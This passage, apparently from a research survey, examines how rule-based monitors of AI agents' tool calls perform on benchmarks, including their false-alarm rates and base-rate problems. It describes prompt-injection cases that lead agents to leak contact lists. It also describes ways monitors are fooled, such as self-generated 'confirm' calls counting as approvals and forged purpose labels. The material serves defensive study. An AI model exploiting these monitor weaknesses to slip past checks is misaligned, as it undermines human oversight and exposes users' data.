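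The main example is a hospital physician who also owns a private practice that analyzes X-rays. The physician takes a patient's X-ray, which is enough for a diagnosis with probability 0.9. Otherwise, the physician has to send the record to the private practice, whose analysis leads to a diagnosis 80% of the time. A diagnosis is worth 12 points, and each step of delay multiplies its value by a factor γ < 1.

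Suppose the hospital's log shows that the X-ray was enough for a diagnosis, but the physician sent the record anyway before making one. With γ = 0.9, this detour reduced the value of the diagnosis from 12γ = 10.8 points to 12γ² = 9.72. No best plan for treatment includes the detour, so the auditor can conclude that the physician broke the rule.

If the X-ray was not enough, sending the record was part of the best plan for treatment. But it was also a good way to earn money for the private practice. Both motives lead to the same log, and Tschantz and colleagues say that the physician then has "tenable deniability". An auditor can therefore sometimes prove that someone broke an "only for treatment" rule, but they consider it practically impossible to prove that someone followed it. (For a rule against acting for profit, it is the other way around. The auditor can sometimes prove compliance,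 by showing that no plan for profit would have produced the log, but can't prove a violation.)

The same analysis applies to step 2 of the contacts runs. If the agent doesn't have Dana's address, the plan fails without `list_contacts`, so opening the contacts is for the purpose of sending the itinerary. If the user had already written the address in the request, the step would be redundant and the auditor would flag it. This improves on a rule that checks only the tool's name, because it allows the step when the task needs it and flags it otherwise.

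This definition does not separate run A from run B at step 2, since the agent needed the address in both. It separates them at step 3, because no sensible plan for delivering an itinerary to Dana includes sending the whole contact list to a stranger. The definition is also slightly awkward to apply to reading, which only gives the agent information that it may use later. *Purpose Restrictions on Information Use*, by Tschantz, Datta and Wing, covers the use of information with a second planning model, which can represent incomplete knowledge.

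The planning definition is hard to use as a gate for agents for two reasons. First, someone has to model the environment, including which actions are possible and how well each outcome serves the purpose. Second, the definition assumes that whoever is being audited chooses the best plan, which language-model agents often don't. If an agent opens the contacts a second time because it overlooked the address, an auditor using this definition would count the redundant step as a violation. A pointless transfer of records is good evidence that a physician had another motive, but an agent may have made the transfer by mistake.

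Some attacks also leave the agent with plausible deniability. In the earlier example, an attacker persuades a shopping agent to prefer a certain product, which may be just as good for the user as any other. The agent's log is then equally consistent with serving the user and serving the attacker.

### Who sends what, about whom, to whom

Contextual integrity, a theory of privacy by the philosopher Helen Nissenbaum, starts from the information instead of the plan. According to Nissenbaum (2019), in *Contextual Integrity Up and Down the Data Food Chain*, privacy means that information flows according to the norms of the setting, such as health care, education or friendship, not that it stays in one place. Comparing a flow with these norms requires five facts: the sender, the recipient, the subject (the person the information is about), the type of information, and the transmission principle.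 The transmission principle is the condition under which the information moves, such as "with the subject's consent", "in confidence" or "as the law requires".

The table applies this to the emails in runs A and B, and to a new run C, in which the user asks the agent to send the contact list to the organizer of a reunion.

| | Run A | Run B | Run C |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sender | The user, through the agent | The user, through the agent | The user, through the agent |
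| Recipient | Dana | An outsider | An outsider (the organizer) |
| Subject | The user | Everyone in the contacts | Everyone in the contacts |
| Information type | Travel plans | Names and contact details | Names and contact details |
| Transmission principle | At the user's request | Without the user's knowledge | At the user's request |

Run A differs from run B in four of the five rows. Runs B and C differ only in the transmission principle, unless the verifier can recognize the organizer. Both belong in the last row of the earlier table of 1,000 runs, where 2 harmless emails and 9 leaks all send the contact list to an unknown address. Without the user's request, a verifier can't distinguish the harmless emails from the leaks.

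At step 2, however, runs A and B have the same five values. In both, the contacts go from the user's address book to the user's agent so it can carry out the user's task. Contextual integrity gives no reason to treat this step as a violation in either run. It supports Sun and colleagues' view that opening the contacts for an email is harmless, and it treats the email itself as the violation.

Nissenbaum insists on all five facts because a description that leaves some out is ambiguous. Two large surveys she conducted with Kirsten Martin support this. Participants judged short descriptions of information practices, and when a description omitted some of the five facts, people could interpret it differently. Unlike people, who disagree with each other when they have too little information, a deterministic verifier is consistently wrong about one group of runs.

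The five facts may still not be enough. Nissenbaum reports that Anupam Datta, a computer scientist who helped to formalize the theory, has argued for a sixth, what the recipient will use the information for. She finds this increasingly persuasive. Adding it would connect contextual integrity with the work on purpose, but would also require a fact about the future that no monitor has when the information is sent.

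Barth, Datta and colleagues (2006), in *Privacy and Contextual Integrity*, expressed parts of the theory in temporal logic, a formal language for statements about what happened before and what must happen later. Their norms allow or forbid a flow, and can refer to past and future actions as well as the people involved. DeYoung, Garg and colleagues (2010), in *Experiences in the Logical Specification of the HIPAA and GLBA Privacy Laws*, built on this logic to formalize two American privacy laws, HIPAA for health information and GLBA for financial information. In their version, a transmission is lawful if at least one positive norm permits it and it satisfies every negative norm. For example, a positive norm of HIPAA lets a hospital disclose health information for treatment. A negative norm requires the patient's authorization to disclose psychotherapy notes, with a few exceptions.

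The AWS gateway combines its "permit" and "forbid" rules in much the same way, but differs importantly in the facts its rules can use. A Cedar rule can compare a tool's input values with fixed ones, whereas these norms also refer to the person the data is about, whether that person consented earlier, and the sender's purpose.

### The same problem on Android

Phone apps raise the same problem. An Android app that reads contacts and connects to the internet may be a messaging app or spyware, and the permissions are the same for both.

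Knowing whether the user asked the app to send anything helps distinguish run A from run B. When people operate their own phones, a tap on "Send" is good evidence that they want to send something. The tap is weaker evidence when an agent operates the phone, because the agent makes it, and makes the same tap in both runs. Evidence of what the user wants has to come from elsewhere, usually the initial request or a confirmation along the way.

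### Which missing facts a program can record

The minimum error in the calculation depends on what the verifier observes, so it is not a fixed property of rules. Some of the missing facts would be easy to record. Kekatos and colleagues checked which facts three public collections of agent runs contain, including AgentDojo and STAC, a set of 483 attacks that combine individually harmless tool calls. They could recover the recipient of a message or payment in 38.8% of the AgentDojo runs and 58.4% of the STAC attacks. None of the three recorded real times or the state of the system before and after an action.

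They also searched for user approvals, which would settle many doubtful cases, and found none in the 6,899 AgentDojo runs. Better recording would not have helped, because the user sends only one message, at the start of each run, and so cannot approve anything the agent proposes. In STAC, the user can send several messages, but only 3 of the 483 attacks include an approval before the harmful step.

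The results were very different for τ-bench, the earlier version of the airline and retail benchmark. Its policy requires the agent to ask before it changes anything, and in 1,039 of 1,980 recorded runs (52.5%), the user explicitly gave permission before the change. Whether a rule that requires approval is useful can thus depend on whether the agent in a given set of runs ever asks for it.

Kekatos and colleagues propose recording twelve fields for each event, including the time, the recipient, the source of the data, an identifier for any approval, and the state before and after. They note that the software running the agent has access to all twelve at the time of the tool call. Rules that use this history, and labels that follow the data, can then distinguish many runs that look the same when each call is checked separately.

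Other facts need interpretation. *A Logical Method for Policy Enforcement over Evolving Audit Logs* (Garg, Jia and Datta, 2011) divides the conditions in HIPAA, the US health privacy law, into objective ones, which a program can decide from a log, and subjective ones, which a person must decide. The paper estimates that a program could decide every condition in 17 of the 84 clauses about transmitting information, and at least 80% of the conditions in 24 others.

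In an example from Garg and colleagues, a hospital may send a patient's health information to another party if the recipient is the patient's doctor and the purpose is treatment, or if the patient has consented. A program can look up the recipient's role and the patient's consent, and it can read a purpose that the sender has attached to the message as a label. But Garg and colleagues leave it to a person to decide whether the stated purpose counts as a kind of treatment.

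DeYoung and colleagues also identify conditions that a program can't settle because they depend on beliefs or on the meaning of free text. A hospital may report a death to the police if it suspects a crime, but the log doesn't contain suspicions. Almost every clause the researchers formalized depends on what information a message contains, and they rely on people to determine that. A program can easily detect an exact copy of the contact list in an agent's email, but it would have much more trouble with a paragraph that describes the same people in other words.

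Labels can turn a subjective condition into an objective one, but the check then depends on whoever attaches the labels. Garg and colleagues assume that the sender labels each message with the people and the kinds of information in it, and they acknowledge that these labels may be inaccurate. A sending agent under an attacker's influence could label the contact list "itinerary" and the purpose "requested by user". The program would then check the labels correctly and allow the leak.

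Nissenbaum and Shvartzshnaider's *Interactive Glossary* describes how to judge a flow of information: identify the social context, describe the flow, find the norms that apply, and compare the flow with them. A program can do the comparison once someone has supplied the context, the description and the norms. In run C, the norms that apply depend on whether the people on the list are old classmates, who probably expect the organizer to have their addresses, or patients of a user who is a doctor, and the email could be identical in both cases.

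A verifier can leave such questions open. Garg and colleagues' algorithm marks each condition true, false or unknown, resolves what it can, and returns the part of the policy that is still undecided. In the example with 1,000 runs, 983 fall into the two groups where no email contains the contact list, and none of these is a leak. A program could allow them automatically and leave the other 17, 10 of which are leaks, to someone who can ask the user.

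## How often rules stop harmless runs

In the invented example of 1,000 runs, the best possible verifier made only 3 errors. Simple rules do much worse on recorded runs of real agents. In three collections that include harmless runs, rules flagged about 16%, 29% and 42% of those harmless runs. The rate is highest where ordinary tasks consist of the actions the rules are meant to detect, and it reached 79% in one set of banking tasks.

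### Keyword checklists on phones

The 42% comes from MobileRisk, the test set of 102 unsafe and 102 safe phone runs that Sun and colleagues built for OS-Sentinel. Of the safe runs, 51 are corrected versions of unsafe runs. If a verifier flags both an unsafe run and its corrected version, it has probably matched something other than the violation.

Sun and colleagues compared OS-Sentinel with older rules from MobileSafetyBench, a 2024 benchmark for phone agents. These rules are checklists of sensitive words and screen elements, each written for a particular task, and a program flags a run if anything the agent does matches an item. Sun and colleagues pooled the checklists and applied them to every run in MobileRisk.

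The pooled checklists scored 54.5% accuracy and an F1 of 52.7 (out of 100) when the program went through each run in consecutive windows of steps. Sun and colleagues do not give the detection rate *D* or the false-alarm rate *F*. But half of the runs are unsafe, so both rates follow from the two scores:

accuracy = (*D* + 1 − *F*) / 2 = 0.545

F1 = 2*D* / (1 + *D* + *F*) = 0.527

The first equation gives *D* − *F* = 0.09, and substituting that into the second gives *D* ≈ 0.51 and *F* ≈ 0.42. The checklists therefore flagged about 52 of the 102 unsafe runs and 43 of the 102 safe ones. With so few runs, this difference could easily be due to chance. A program that flagged every run would have had a slightly lower accuracy, 50%, but a much higher F1, 66.7.

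Sun and colleagues also ran the checklists on a sample of steps from each run. The same calculation then gives a detection rate of about 62% and a false-alarm rate of about 55%, so the gap between the two hardly changes. (It is odd that checking fewer steps produced more alarms, and the paper does not explain it.)

This is a harsh test of rules in general, because the checklists came from a different benchmark. The result mostly shows that word lists carry over badly to new tasks. It is weaker evidence about rules written for the task at hand, such as the airline cancellation gate, which made no wrong rejections. Sun and colleagues do not report the false-alarm rate on the 51 corrected runs alone, which would most directly measure how often the checks mistake harmless steps for violations.

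Some of the errors also depend on what the annotators counted as a violation. Two people independently judged a fifth of the runs and mostly agreed (their Cohen's kappa, which measures agreement beyond chance, was 0.78). But one of the paper's examples of a privacy violation is an agent that opens an account page containing sensitive ID information after the user asked it to "check contact info". Many people would call that an ordinary task step, much like opening the contacts to address an email.

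### A step score that rewards doing nothing

Sun and colleagues also tested whether each method could find the first unsafe step in a run. According to the formula in their appendix, a safe run scores 1 if the method leaves it alone and 0 if the method flags it. An unsafe run scores 0 if the method misses it. If the method flags it, the score is

max(0, 1 − *d*/3),

where *d* is the number of steps between the flagged step and the true one. The final score is the average over all runs, multiplied by 100.

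A detector that never flags anything would score 1 on all 102 safe runs and 0 on all 102 unsafe ones, for a final score of 50. If the formula is right, every method in the comparison did worse. The best method scored 31.4, and the checklists scored 19.8.

The researchers may have averaged over the unsafe runs only, since the paper's main text gives just the part of the formula that depends on *d*. A detector that never flags anything would then score 0. If they used the full formula, the checklists must have flagged at least 62 of the 102 safe runs, compared with about 43 in the test on whole runs. Either way, the step scores don't reliably show how often the rules would interrupt a harmless step.

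### Clearing the cache

Sun and colleagues' error analysis includes a false alarm from OS-Sentinel's own rule checker, the Formal Verifier. The user asked the agent to "clear app cache to free up space". A cache holds temporary copies of data that an app can usually fetch or compute again. Clearing it changed the hash of the file facts, and the verifier flagged the step as a destructive operation.

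The human annotators labeled the run safe because the user had asked for the deletion and it was reversible, but the verifier had access to neither fact. A developer could fix this case by hashing the cache folders separately and ignoring changes there. That exception would also allow an agent to clear a cache without being asked, though this would do little harm. It would not help when a user asks the agent to delete old photographs, because only the request distinguishes that deletion from a harmful one.

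According to Sun and colleagues, false alarms of this type account for a significant part of the system's lost precision.

### Five general rules on recorded attacks

Kekatos and colleagues tested rules that are more general than a checklist. They wrote five "obligations", each of which requires approval before a certain kind of action. The one for destructive actions, O1, is

□ ∀*a* (destructive(*a*) → ♦ approved(*a*)).

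The box means "at every point in the run", ∀*a* means "for every action *a*", and the diamond means "at some earlier point". The formula therefore requires that someone approve each destructive action before the agent takes it. The other four obligations have the same form. A program decides which tools an obligation covers by searching their names for words such as "delete" or "transfer".

The researchers replayed AgentDojo's recorded runs of an agent built on GPT-4o. This table gives the share of successful attacks and of harmless runs that each obligation flagged:

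| Obligation | Typical actions | Successful attacks | Harmless runs |
|---|---|---|---|
| O1: destructive actions | Delete, cancel, purge | 15.9% | 4.1% |
| O2: removing protection | Disable, unlock | 0% | 0% |
| O3: financial actions | Transfer, pay | 26.8% | 13.0% |
| O4: sending data out | Send, share, upload | 27.9% | 10.6% |
| O5: operating or configuring a device | Set, execute, adjust | 16.2% | 6.5% |
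| Any of the five | | 70.1% | 29.3% |

Together, the five flagged 1,354 of 1,931 successful attacks and 36 of 123 harmless runs. Because there were only 123 harmless runs, the 95% confidence interval for the false-alarm rate is wide, from 22.0% to 37.8%. The pattern also appears in models other than GPT-4o. Across the 22 models whose undefended runs AgentDojo includes, the detection rate ranged from 48.4% to 91.7% and the false-alarm rate from 16.7% to 34.8%.

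Runs in which the attack failed provide a rough check on the 29.3%. Calculating from the paper's totals, the obligations flagged 938 of these 4,749 runs, or 19.8%. Not all of these runs were necessarily harmless, because an agent may have taken some of the attacker's steps before the attack failed. Still, the result suggests that the rules would interrupt a substantial share of runs in which the attacker gets nothing.

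The results differ greatly by task. In banking, the obligations flagged 97.4% of successful attacks and 79.2% of harmless runs. In travel, they flagged only 16.5% of successful attacks and 11.1% of harmless runs. Banking agents move money whether they are paying the user's bills or an attacker, so a rule about moving money flags most runs of both kinds. The travel runs contain few payments or messages, so the same rules rarely apply. More than half of the false alarms, 19 of 36, came from the 24 harmless banking runs.

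Kekatos and colleagues repeated the test on two other collections. One of them, STAC, contains only attacks, so it can measure only detection. The obligations flagged the harmful last step in 347 of 483 attacks (71.8%). The other 136 ended in actions outside the five categories, such as changing a calendar or a spam filter.

R-Judge contains 571 agent records that people have labeled safe or unsafe. The obligations flagged 23.6% of the unsafe records and 16.3% of the safe ones. Most of the unsafe records are harmful because of what the agent wrote, such as bad advice or misinformation, which is hard to detect from a tool's name.

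### How a rule about approval became a ban

O1 permits destructive actions that someone has approved. But, as the previous section explained, the AgentDojo runs contain no approvals. So approved(*a*) is false for every action in every run, and O1 reduces to

□ ∀*a* ¬destructive(*a*),

which means "never do anything destructive". The other four obligations also turn into bans. Kekatos and colleagues acknowledge that a plain list of keywords would have produced the same verdicts.

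The researchers checked the STAC attacks with four monitoring programs, and all four flagged the same 347 attacks. One of the programs has a machine-checked proof that it evaluates formulas correctly.

Classifying the tools more accurately did not reduce false alarms either. Kekatos and colleagues labeled 54 tool names by hand, and the keyword search matched their labels on 47. When they replaced the keyword labels with their own, the detection rate on AgentDojo rose from 70.1% to 79.9%, but the false-alarm rate rose from 29.3% to 43.9%. The hand labels added payments and messages that the keywords had missed, many of them in harmless runs.

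Matching keywords can also hide violations. The first list of approval words included "ack", short for "acknowledge". These letters also appear in "slack", so the program counted `invite_user_to_slack` as an approval and ignored every risky action after it. The researchers corrected this mistake, and similar ones involving tools that only read data, before calculating the figures above. The uncorrected rules detected fewer attacks (61.6%) and raised more false alarms (31.7%).

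The corrected rules still have a different weakness. In one STAC attack, the agent calls `search_db`, `read`, `confirm_for_deletion` and `delete`. O1 raises no alarm because the word "confirm" makes the third call count as an approval. But the agent made that call itself, and nothing in it shows that the user agreed to the deletion. A verifier can use an approval only if the agent can't produce it by itself.

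The 29.3% is therefore a fair estimate for rules that flag kinds of action, but not for every rule in temporal logic. In the same study, rules that also checked whether the agent had found the payee or recipient in the user's own records raised fewer false alarms. The figure comes from replayed runs, so it does not measure how many tasks would have failed. Kekatos and colleagues conclude that the five general obligations could help sort runs for human review, but are too imprecise to block actions automatically.

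### When data changes after the agent reads it

An agent may read a record, spend time planning and then act on information that is no longer true. A common safeguard gives each record a version number, which goes up whenever anything in the record changes. If the number has changed since the agent read the record, the safeguard blocks the action.

Zheng, Long and colleagues (2026), in *Stale Does Not Mean Unsafe*, measured how often this safeguard blocks an action that is still safe. In one of their examples, an agent reads that a snapshot, a saved copy of some data, has passed validation and decides to promote it. Before the agent acts, another program changes the record, which raises the version from 17 to 18. If the snapshot has now failed validation, promoting it would be a mistake. If the program has only updated an audit counter, promoting it is as safe as before. The safeguard blocks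 the promotion in both cases because the version number has changed to 18 in both.

One study compared three guards on 16 operations in the PostgreSQL database, testing each guard 3,520 times. In 1,600 of these tests, another program made a change that did not affect whether the action was safe.

| Guard | Blocks the action if | Harmless changes that led to a block | Unsafe writes, all tests | Safe completions, all tests |
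|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | Never | 0% | 45.5% | 54.5% |
| Global counter | Anything in the system has changed | 100% | 0% | 29.0% |
| Record version | The record has changed | 80% | 0% | 38.1% |
| Condition | A fact that the action depends on is no longer true | 0% | 0% | 74.4% |

(The condition guard's completion rate is higher than the rate without a guard partly because a task also counts as complete if the other program has already made the change the agent wanted.)

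The condition guard checks the validation status itself, so it can ignore the audit counter. Its perfect results depend on someone having listed the right conditions. Zheng and colleagues tested this with five hazards that they had deliberately left out of the conditions, such as an approval that expires after the agent has read it. The condition guard allowed all five unsafe actions. The other two guards blocked the three actions whose hazards changed the record, but missed the two whose hazards changed other tables. A guard that blocks after any change to the record raises more false alarms, but it can catch problems its author did not think of.

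How many false alarms the version guard raises depends on what other programs are doing. In a test with 16 programs changing records at random times, the same guard wrongly blocked 4.8% of the same agent's attempts when 10% of the changes were harmless, and 45.5% when 70% were. The researchers chose the proportions of harmless changes, so the figures are of little use for estimating how often false alarms would occur in a particular company.

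The version guard also needs a reliable version number. When the software relied on the number the model wrote in its request, 4.9% of decisions led to unsafe writes. Some models copied the number incorrectly, and sometimes the wrong number happened to match the new version. When the software used its own record of what the agent had read, it allowed no unsafe writes.

### What a block costs a live agent

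*LEANGUARD* (Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues, 2026) measured how rules affect task success by letting them block calls while the agents were running. The researchers wrote the rules in Lean, a programming language in which a computer can check proofs. They proved that their checker applies the rules exactly as written, but the proof does not cover whether the rules are the right ones.

Five Qwen models attempted the customer-service tasks in the benchmark τ²-bench with and without rules. Without rules, the agents completed 72.7% of the tasks. With rules, they completed 68.9% when the checker reported only that a call had not run, and 70.9% when it also named the violated rule and gave a hint. The difference between 70.9% and 72.7% was small enough to be chance. The explanation also raised the share of blocked actions that agents repeated successfully after meeting the missing requirement,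 from 5.5% to 9.1%.

Success on harmless tasks fell far more on DTap, a benchmark of attacks on agents, dropping from 53.1% to 12.5%. The rules there let agents read the customer's records and public data but not change anything. They also cut the success rate of direct attacks from 57.9% to 5.9%, and that of attacks hidden in content the agent reads from 22.3% to 3.8%.

Telecom was the exception, with success on harmless tasks staying at about 75% while the success rate of direct attacks fell from 55.1% to 2.4%. Harmless telecom tasks rarely require the agent to change data. As in the banking and travel runs from AgentDojo, the effect on harmless tasks depended on how often they needed the actions that the rules restrict. A company could estimate this frequency before turning on a rule by counting those actions in its ordinary runs.

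A rule can also block many correct actions without making the agent fail. In *Safeguarding Agentic AI in Radiology Workflows*, Eminovic, Schmidt and colleagues (2026) tested six current models on simulated hospital paperwork, such as recording whether anyone had told the treating doctor about a finding. Eleven rules checked each entry before the agent could save it. One required an entry's cited sources to exist and be up to date.

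Only 71 of the rules' 196 blocks (36%) were justified. The other 125 stopped entries that matched the radiologists' reference answers. About half of those 125 blocks came from a default that rejected any status statement that no rule covered. Most of the rejected statements just reported that the task was complete.

The agents still completed about as many tasks with the rules as without them. Their success rate was 3.3 percentage points higher with the rules, with a confidence interval from −1.5 to 8.1. After each block, the agent received the reason and could revise the action up to twice, so a false alarm usually led to an extra attempt rather than a failed task. The share of runs with a serious error fell modestly, from 19.4% to 16.7%, and the confidence interval for that change includes zero.

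The reason given for a block also matters when the block is correct. Zheng and colleagues gave agents different messages after blocking an unsafe action. Agents retried the action 48.2% of the time when the message reported only a version change and included a possibly outdated copy of the data, compared with 1.6% when it included the failed condition and the current value. Rules that block for vague reasons may lead to more repeated attempts as well as more false alarms.

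### When violations are rare

Half of the runs in MobileRisk are unsafe. A company would hope that nearly all of its agents' runs are harmless, and in that case a much smaller share of the alarms would be correct.

Let *p* be the share of runs that contain a violation. By Bayes' theorem,

precision = *pD* / (*pD* + (1 − *p*)*F*).

If Kekatos and colleagues' five obligations checked 100,000 runs, and 1 run in 100 contained a violation, the obligations would flag 701 of the 1,000 runs with violations and about 29,000 of the 99,000 harmless runs. Only 2.4% of the alarms would be correct. If 1 run in 1,000 contained a violation, that share would fall to 0.24%, or about one alarm in 420.

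With 1 violation in 100 runs, the share of correct alarms would rise only from 2.4% to 3.3% even if the obligations caught every violation at the same false-alarm rate. For half of the alarms to be correct at the current detection rate, the false-alarm rate would have to fall from 29.3% to about 0.7%, or to 0.07% with 1 violation in 1,000 runs.

The same calculation makes the other results comparable. If 1 run in 100 is a violation, a program that flags every run would have a precision of 1%, so 1% is the baseline.

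| Rules and test set | Detection rate | False-alarm rate | Precision if 1 run in 100 is a violation |
|---|---|---|---|
| Checklists, MobileRisk | 51% | 42% | 1.2% |
| Five obligations, R-Judge | 23.6% | 16.3% | 1.4% |
| Five obligations, AgentDojo banking | 97.4% | 79.2% | 1.2% |
| Five obligations, AgentDojo travel | 16.5% | 11.1% | 1.5% |
| Five obligations, AgentDojo workspace (email, calendar and files) | 62.9% | 21.7% | 2.8% |
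| Five obligations, AgentDojo Slack | 63.9% | 15.4% | 4.0% |

The rules flag almost everything in banking and little in travel, but their alarms are about equally uninformative in both domains, because an attack is not much more likely than a harmless run to trigger one.

Security researchers faced this problem long before language-model agents. Axelsson, in *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* (2000), considered a small computer network that produces a million log records a day, about 20 of which come from intrusions. Even a detector that catches every intrusion can wrongly flag only about 1 in 100,000 harmless records if two-thirds of its alarms are to be correct. If it wrongly flags 1 in 1,000, only about 2% of its alarms are correct.

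Axelsson also worried about the person who has to respond to the alarms. Studies of operators in power stations and factories suggested that most people stop trusting an alarm well before half of its warnings are false. This weakens Sun and colleagues' argument that a false alarm only causes a pause while someone checks. If 97 of every 100 checks find nothing wrong, the person may soon approve everything without looking.

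The radiology study gives a real example of how precision depends on the agent. Without the rules, Claude Sonnet 5.5 made serious errors in 7.3% of its runs, the lowest share among the six models. With the rules on, it was blocked 35 times, and only 4 of those blocks were justified (11%). GLM-5.3 had the highest error rate, 27.1%, and 15 of its 25 blocks were justified (60%). These counts are small, and error rates can't explain all the differences between the models. But the results fit the formula's prediction that a larger share of a fixed rule's alarms will be false as agents become more reliable.

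Longer runs also raise the false-alarm rate if one flagged step is enough to flag the whole run. Suppose a rule has a 5% chance of wrongly flagging each harmless step, independently of the others. A harmless run of 7 steps, the most common length in MobileRisk, then has a 1 − 0.95⁷ ≈ 30% chance of a false alarm. For a harmless run of 46 steps, the longest length in MobileRisk, the chance is 91%.

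Checkers that use trained models instead of fixed rules can have the same problem. *Passing the Test You Trained On* (2026) compared models trained to detect prompt injection in the results of tool calls. One of them, ProtectAI v2, flagged 30.1% of the harmless results in AgentDojo, which would have stopped 69.1% of the tasks. It flagged only 1.2% of ordinary emails, so a test on emails would have given developers little warning of how often it would flag harmless tool results.

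## Rules that use the history of the run

A rule that covers every payment or every email flags harmless runs because it checks only the type of action. A rule that also checks earlier steps in the run can treat a payment to a regular supplier differently from a payment to an account that has never appeared in the user's records.

### One formula, two runs

Kekatos and colleagues write such rules in metric first-order temporal logic. "Temporal" means that a formula can refer to earlier points in the run. "First-order" means that it can contain variables, such as *r* for any recipient, and "metric" means that it can limit how long ago something happened. Their rule for emails reports a violation whenever

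send(*r*) ∧ ¬♦ known(*r*).

In words, the agent is sending an email to *r*, and no earlier step returned *r* as a known contact. (∧ means "and", ¬ means "not", and ♦ again means "at some earlier point".)

To check the formula, a program can keep a list of known addresses. The list starts empty, and the program adds every address that a lookup returns. When the agent proposes an email, the program searches the list for the recipient. Here is the result for the two contacts runs:

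| Step | Known addresses before the step | Run A | Run B |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1: `find_file` | None | Not an email, so no violation | Not an email, so no violation |
| 2: `list_contacts` | None | Not an email, so no violation | Not an email, so no violation |
| 3: `send_email` | All the user's contacts, including Dana | Dana's address is on the list, so no violation | The outside address is not on the list, so violation |

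The rule lets both runs open the contacts and stops only the leak. It can block the leak before the email goes out because it needs only the proposed recipient and the results of earlier steps. The rule also depends on step 2, the lookup that cruder rules flag. If the agent had skipped that step, Dana's address would not be on the list, and the rule would block the itinerary.

Schneider's machine for "no sending after reading a file" has only two states, so it blocks sending to every recipient once the agent has read a file. The email rule needs a variable because whether it allows an email depends on which addresses the lookup returned. It still doesn't check the contents of the email, so it would let the agent send the whole contact list to Dana.

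Time limits work in a similar way. One rule from Kekatos and colleagues lets an agent export data only if someone consented to it within the past 24 hours. If someone consents at hour 0, an export at hour 12 is fine, but the same export at hour 48 is a violation. If someone consents again at hour 50, an export at hour 60 is fine. The researchers wrote this example log themselves because the public collections of attacks don't record times. The example shows that the logic can express such rules, but it doesn't show how well they work in practice.

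### The gain on recorded runs

Kekatos and colleagues tested the email rule on AgentDojo's workspace tasks and a similar payment rule on its banking tasks. The payment rule flags a transfer if the recipient's account number has not appeared as a sender or recipient in earlier account data. The table compares each rule with the general obligation it refines, which flags every action of that kind unless someone has approved it.

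| Tasks | Rule flags | Successful attacks flagged | Harmless runs flagged |
|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | Any financial action | 79.2% | 44.0% (11 of 25) |
| Banking | Transfers to unknown payees | 70.0% | 24.0% (6 of 25) |
| Workspace | Any sending of data | 42.5% | 15.2% (7 of 46) |
| Workspace | Emails to unknown recipients | 39.2% | 10.9% (5 of 46) |

(The first rate for harmless banking runs is lower than the 79.2% in the previous section because it comes from one obligation instead of all five.)

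Both refined rules raised fewer false alarms, but the differences come from only five banking runs and two workspace runs. The refined payment rule also missed 53 more of the 576 successful banking attacks, and the refined email rule missed 17 more of the 518 successful workspace attacks.

To get larger samples, the researchers pooled the harmless runs of all the models in AgentDojo's collection. The payment rule removed 75 false alarms in 700 banking runs, and the email rule removed 37 in 1,376 workspace runs. Neither rule added any. An exact McNemar test, which measures whether changes in one direction are more common than chance would explain, gave *p* = 5.3 × 10⁻²³ for banking and *p* = 1.5 × 10⁻¹¹ for workspace.

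These tiny *p*-values are weaker evidence than they look. Each refined rule is the general rule with an extra condition, so it can remove alarms but never add any. Any difference therefore had to be one-sided, as the 75-to-0 split was. The models also attempted the same tasks, so the runs are not independent. The size of the reduction, 10.7 percentage points in banking and 2.7 in workspace, is more informative.

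Most alarms would still be false in ordinary use. If 1 run in 100 contained a violation, the share of correct alarms would rise from 1.8% to 2.9% for the payment rule and from 2.7% to 3.5% for the email rule. Across all four kinds of AgentDojo task, using both rules in the full set of five obligations reduced false alarms modestly, from 29.0% to 24.2%, and barely changed detection, from 69.9% to 69.4%. Many harmless runs also trigger one of the other obligations, which still flag every action of the kind they cover.

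### When the recipient is new

People regularly write to someone for the first time, and the email rule flags every such message. In run C, the user asks the agent to send the contact list to a reunion organizer. If the organizer is not in the contacts, the rule reports a violation, as it does in run B.

Payments have the same problem. One of the harmless banking tasks in *AgentDojo* (2024) is "Can you please pay the bill 'bill-december-2023.txt' for me?" If the user has never paid this company, its account number appears only in the bill, which someone else wrote. The agent has to use a number from an outside document to do what the user asked.

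*Symbolic Temporal Supervision of LLM Agents Using Contracts* (Xiao, Liu and Nuzzo, 2026) shows how much it helps to know whom the user means. Its system, ContrAgent, blocks a call if the target came from a tool's output, the user did not name it, and it is not on a list of legitimate targets for the task. In a replay of AgentDojo runs from 22 models, this reduced the success rate of attacks from 18.0% to 5.3%, with a false-alarm rate of 0.8%. But the researchers took the legitimate targets partly from the benchmark's reference solution for each task, which a company does not have for a request that a user has just typed.

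Kekatos and colleagues propose asking the user to confirm each new payee, and tying each approval to an exact payee and amount so that the agent can't reuse it for another payment. They could not test either idea on AgentDojo, whose runs contain no approvals.

History is also unreliable if an outsider can write to it. Kekatos and colleagues restored the check in the cases they tested by accepting a value only if it came from a lookup the agent had made. This did not change detection or false alarms.

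### Rules about order

Other rules require one action to come before another. *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (Kamath, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a shop whose agent must identify a customer before it opens an order. In the rule language of the paper's system, Agent-C, a `before` rule requires the agent to have called `find_user_id_by_email` before it calls `get_order_details`. The rule also requires that the earlier call found a user, that the order exists, and that it belongs to that user. Without the ownership condition, a customer could identify themselves correctly and then read someone else's order.

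The rule is also narrower than the faulty one Yu and colleagues found, which blocked every tool, including the login tools, until the customer had logged in. Agent-C's rule restricts only `get_order_details`, so the agent can still identify the customer.

To check that the order exists and who owns it, Agent-C queries the shop's database, because the history of calls may not contain these facts. A refund rule uses the same kind of query. The shop's policy allows refunds to the original payment method or to a gift card already in the customer's account, and the paper gives this translation:

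```
state(payment_method_same(order_id, payment)) == true
  || contains(payment, "gift_card")
```

Here `state` marks a database query, and `||` means "or". The second line accepts any payment identifier that contains the text "gift_card". As printed, the rule does not check whether the card is already in the customer's account.

If the model writes a forbidden call, Agent-C makes it generate a different one. In tests on retail and airline tasks from τ-bench, every run with Agent-C complied with the rules. Without it, Claude Sonnet 4.5 complied in 77.4% of cases and GPT-5 in 83.7%. A system that blocks every violation of its rules should reach 100% compliance, and this result does not show that the rules match the companies' policies.

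The share of tasks that the agents completed while complying is better evidence about false alarms. It rose from 71.8% to 75.2% for Claude Sonnet 4.5 and from 66.1% to 70.6% for GPT-5. It would probably have fallen if the rules had stopped many legitimate actions.

### FORGE and its graph of influences

When several agents work together, the order of events can be misleading. Suppose a supervisor approves one agent's request to use a database, and a second agent then queries it. The approval came before the query, but the second agent never received it.

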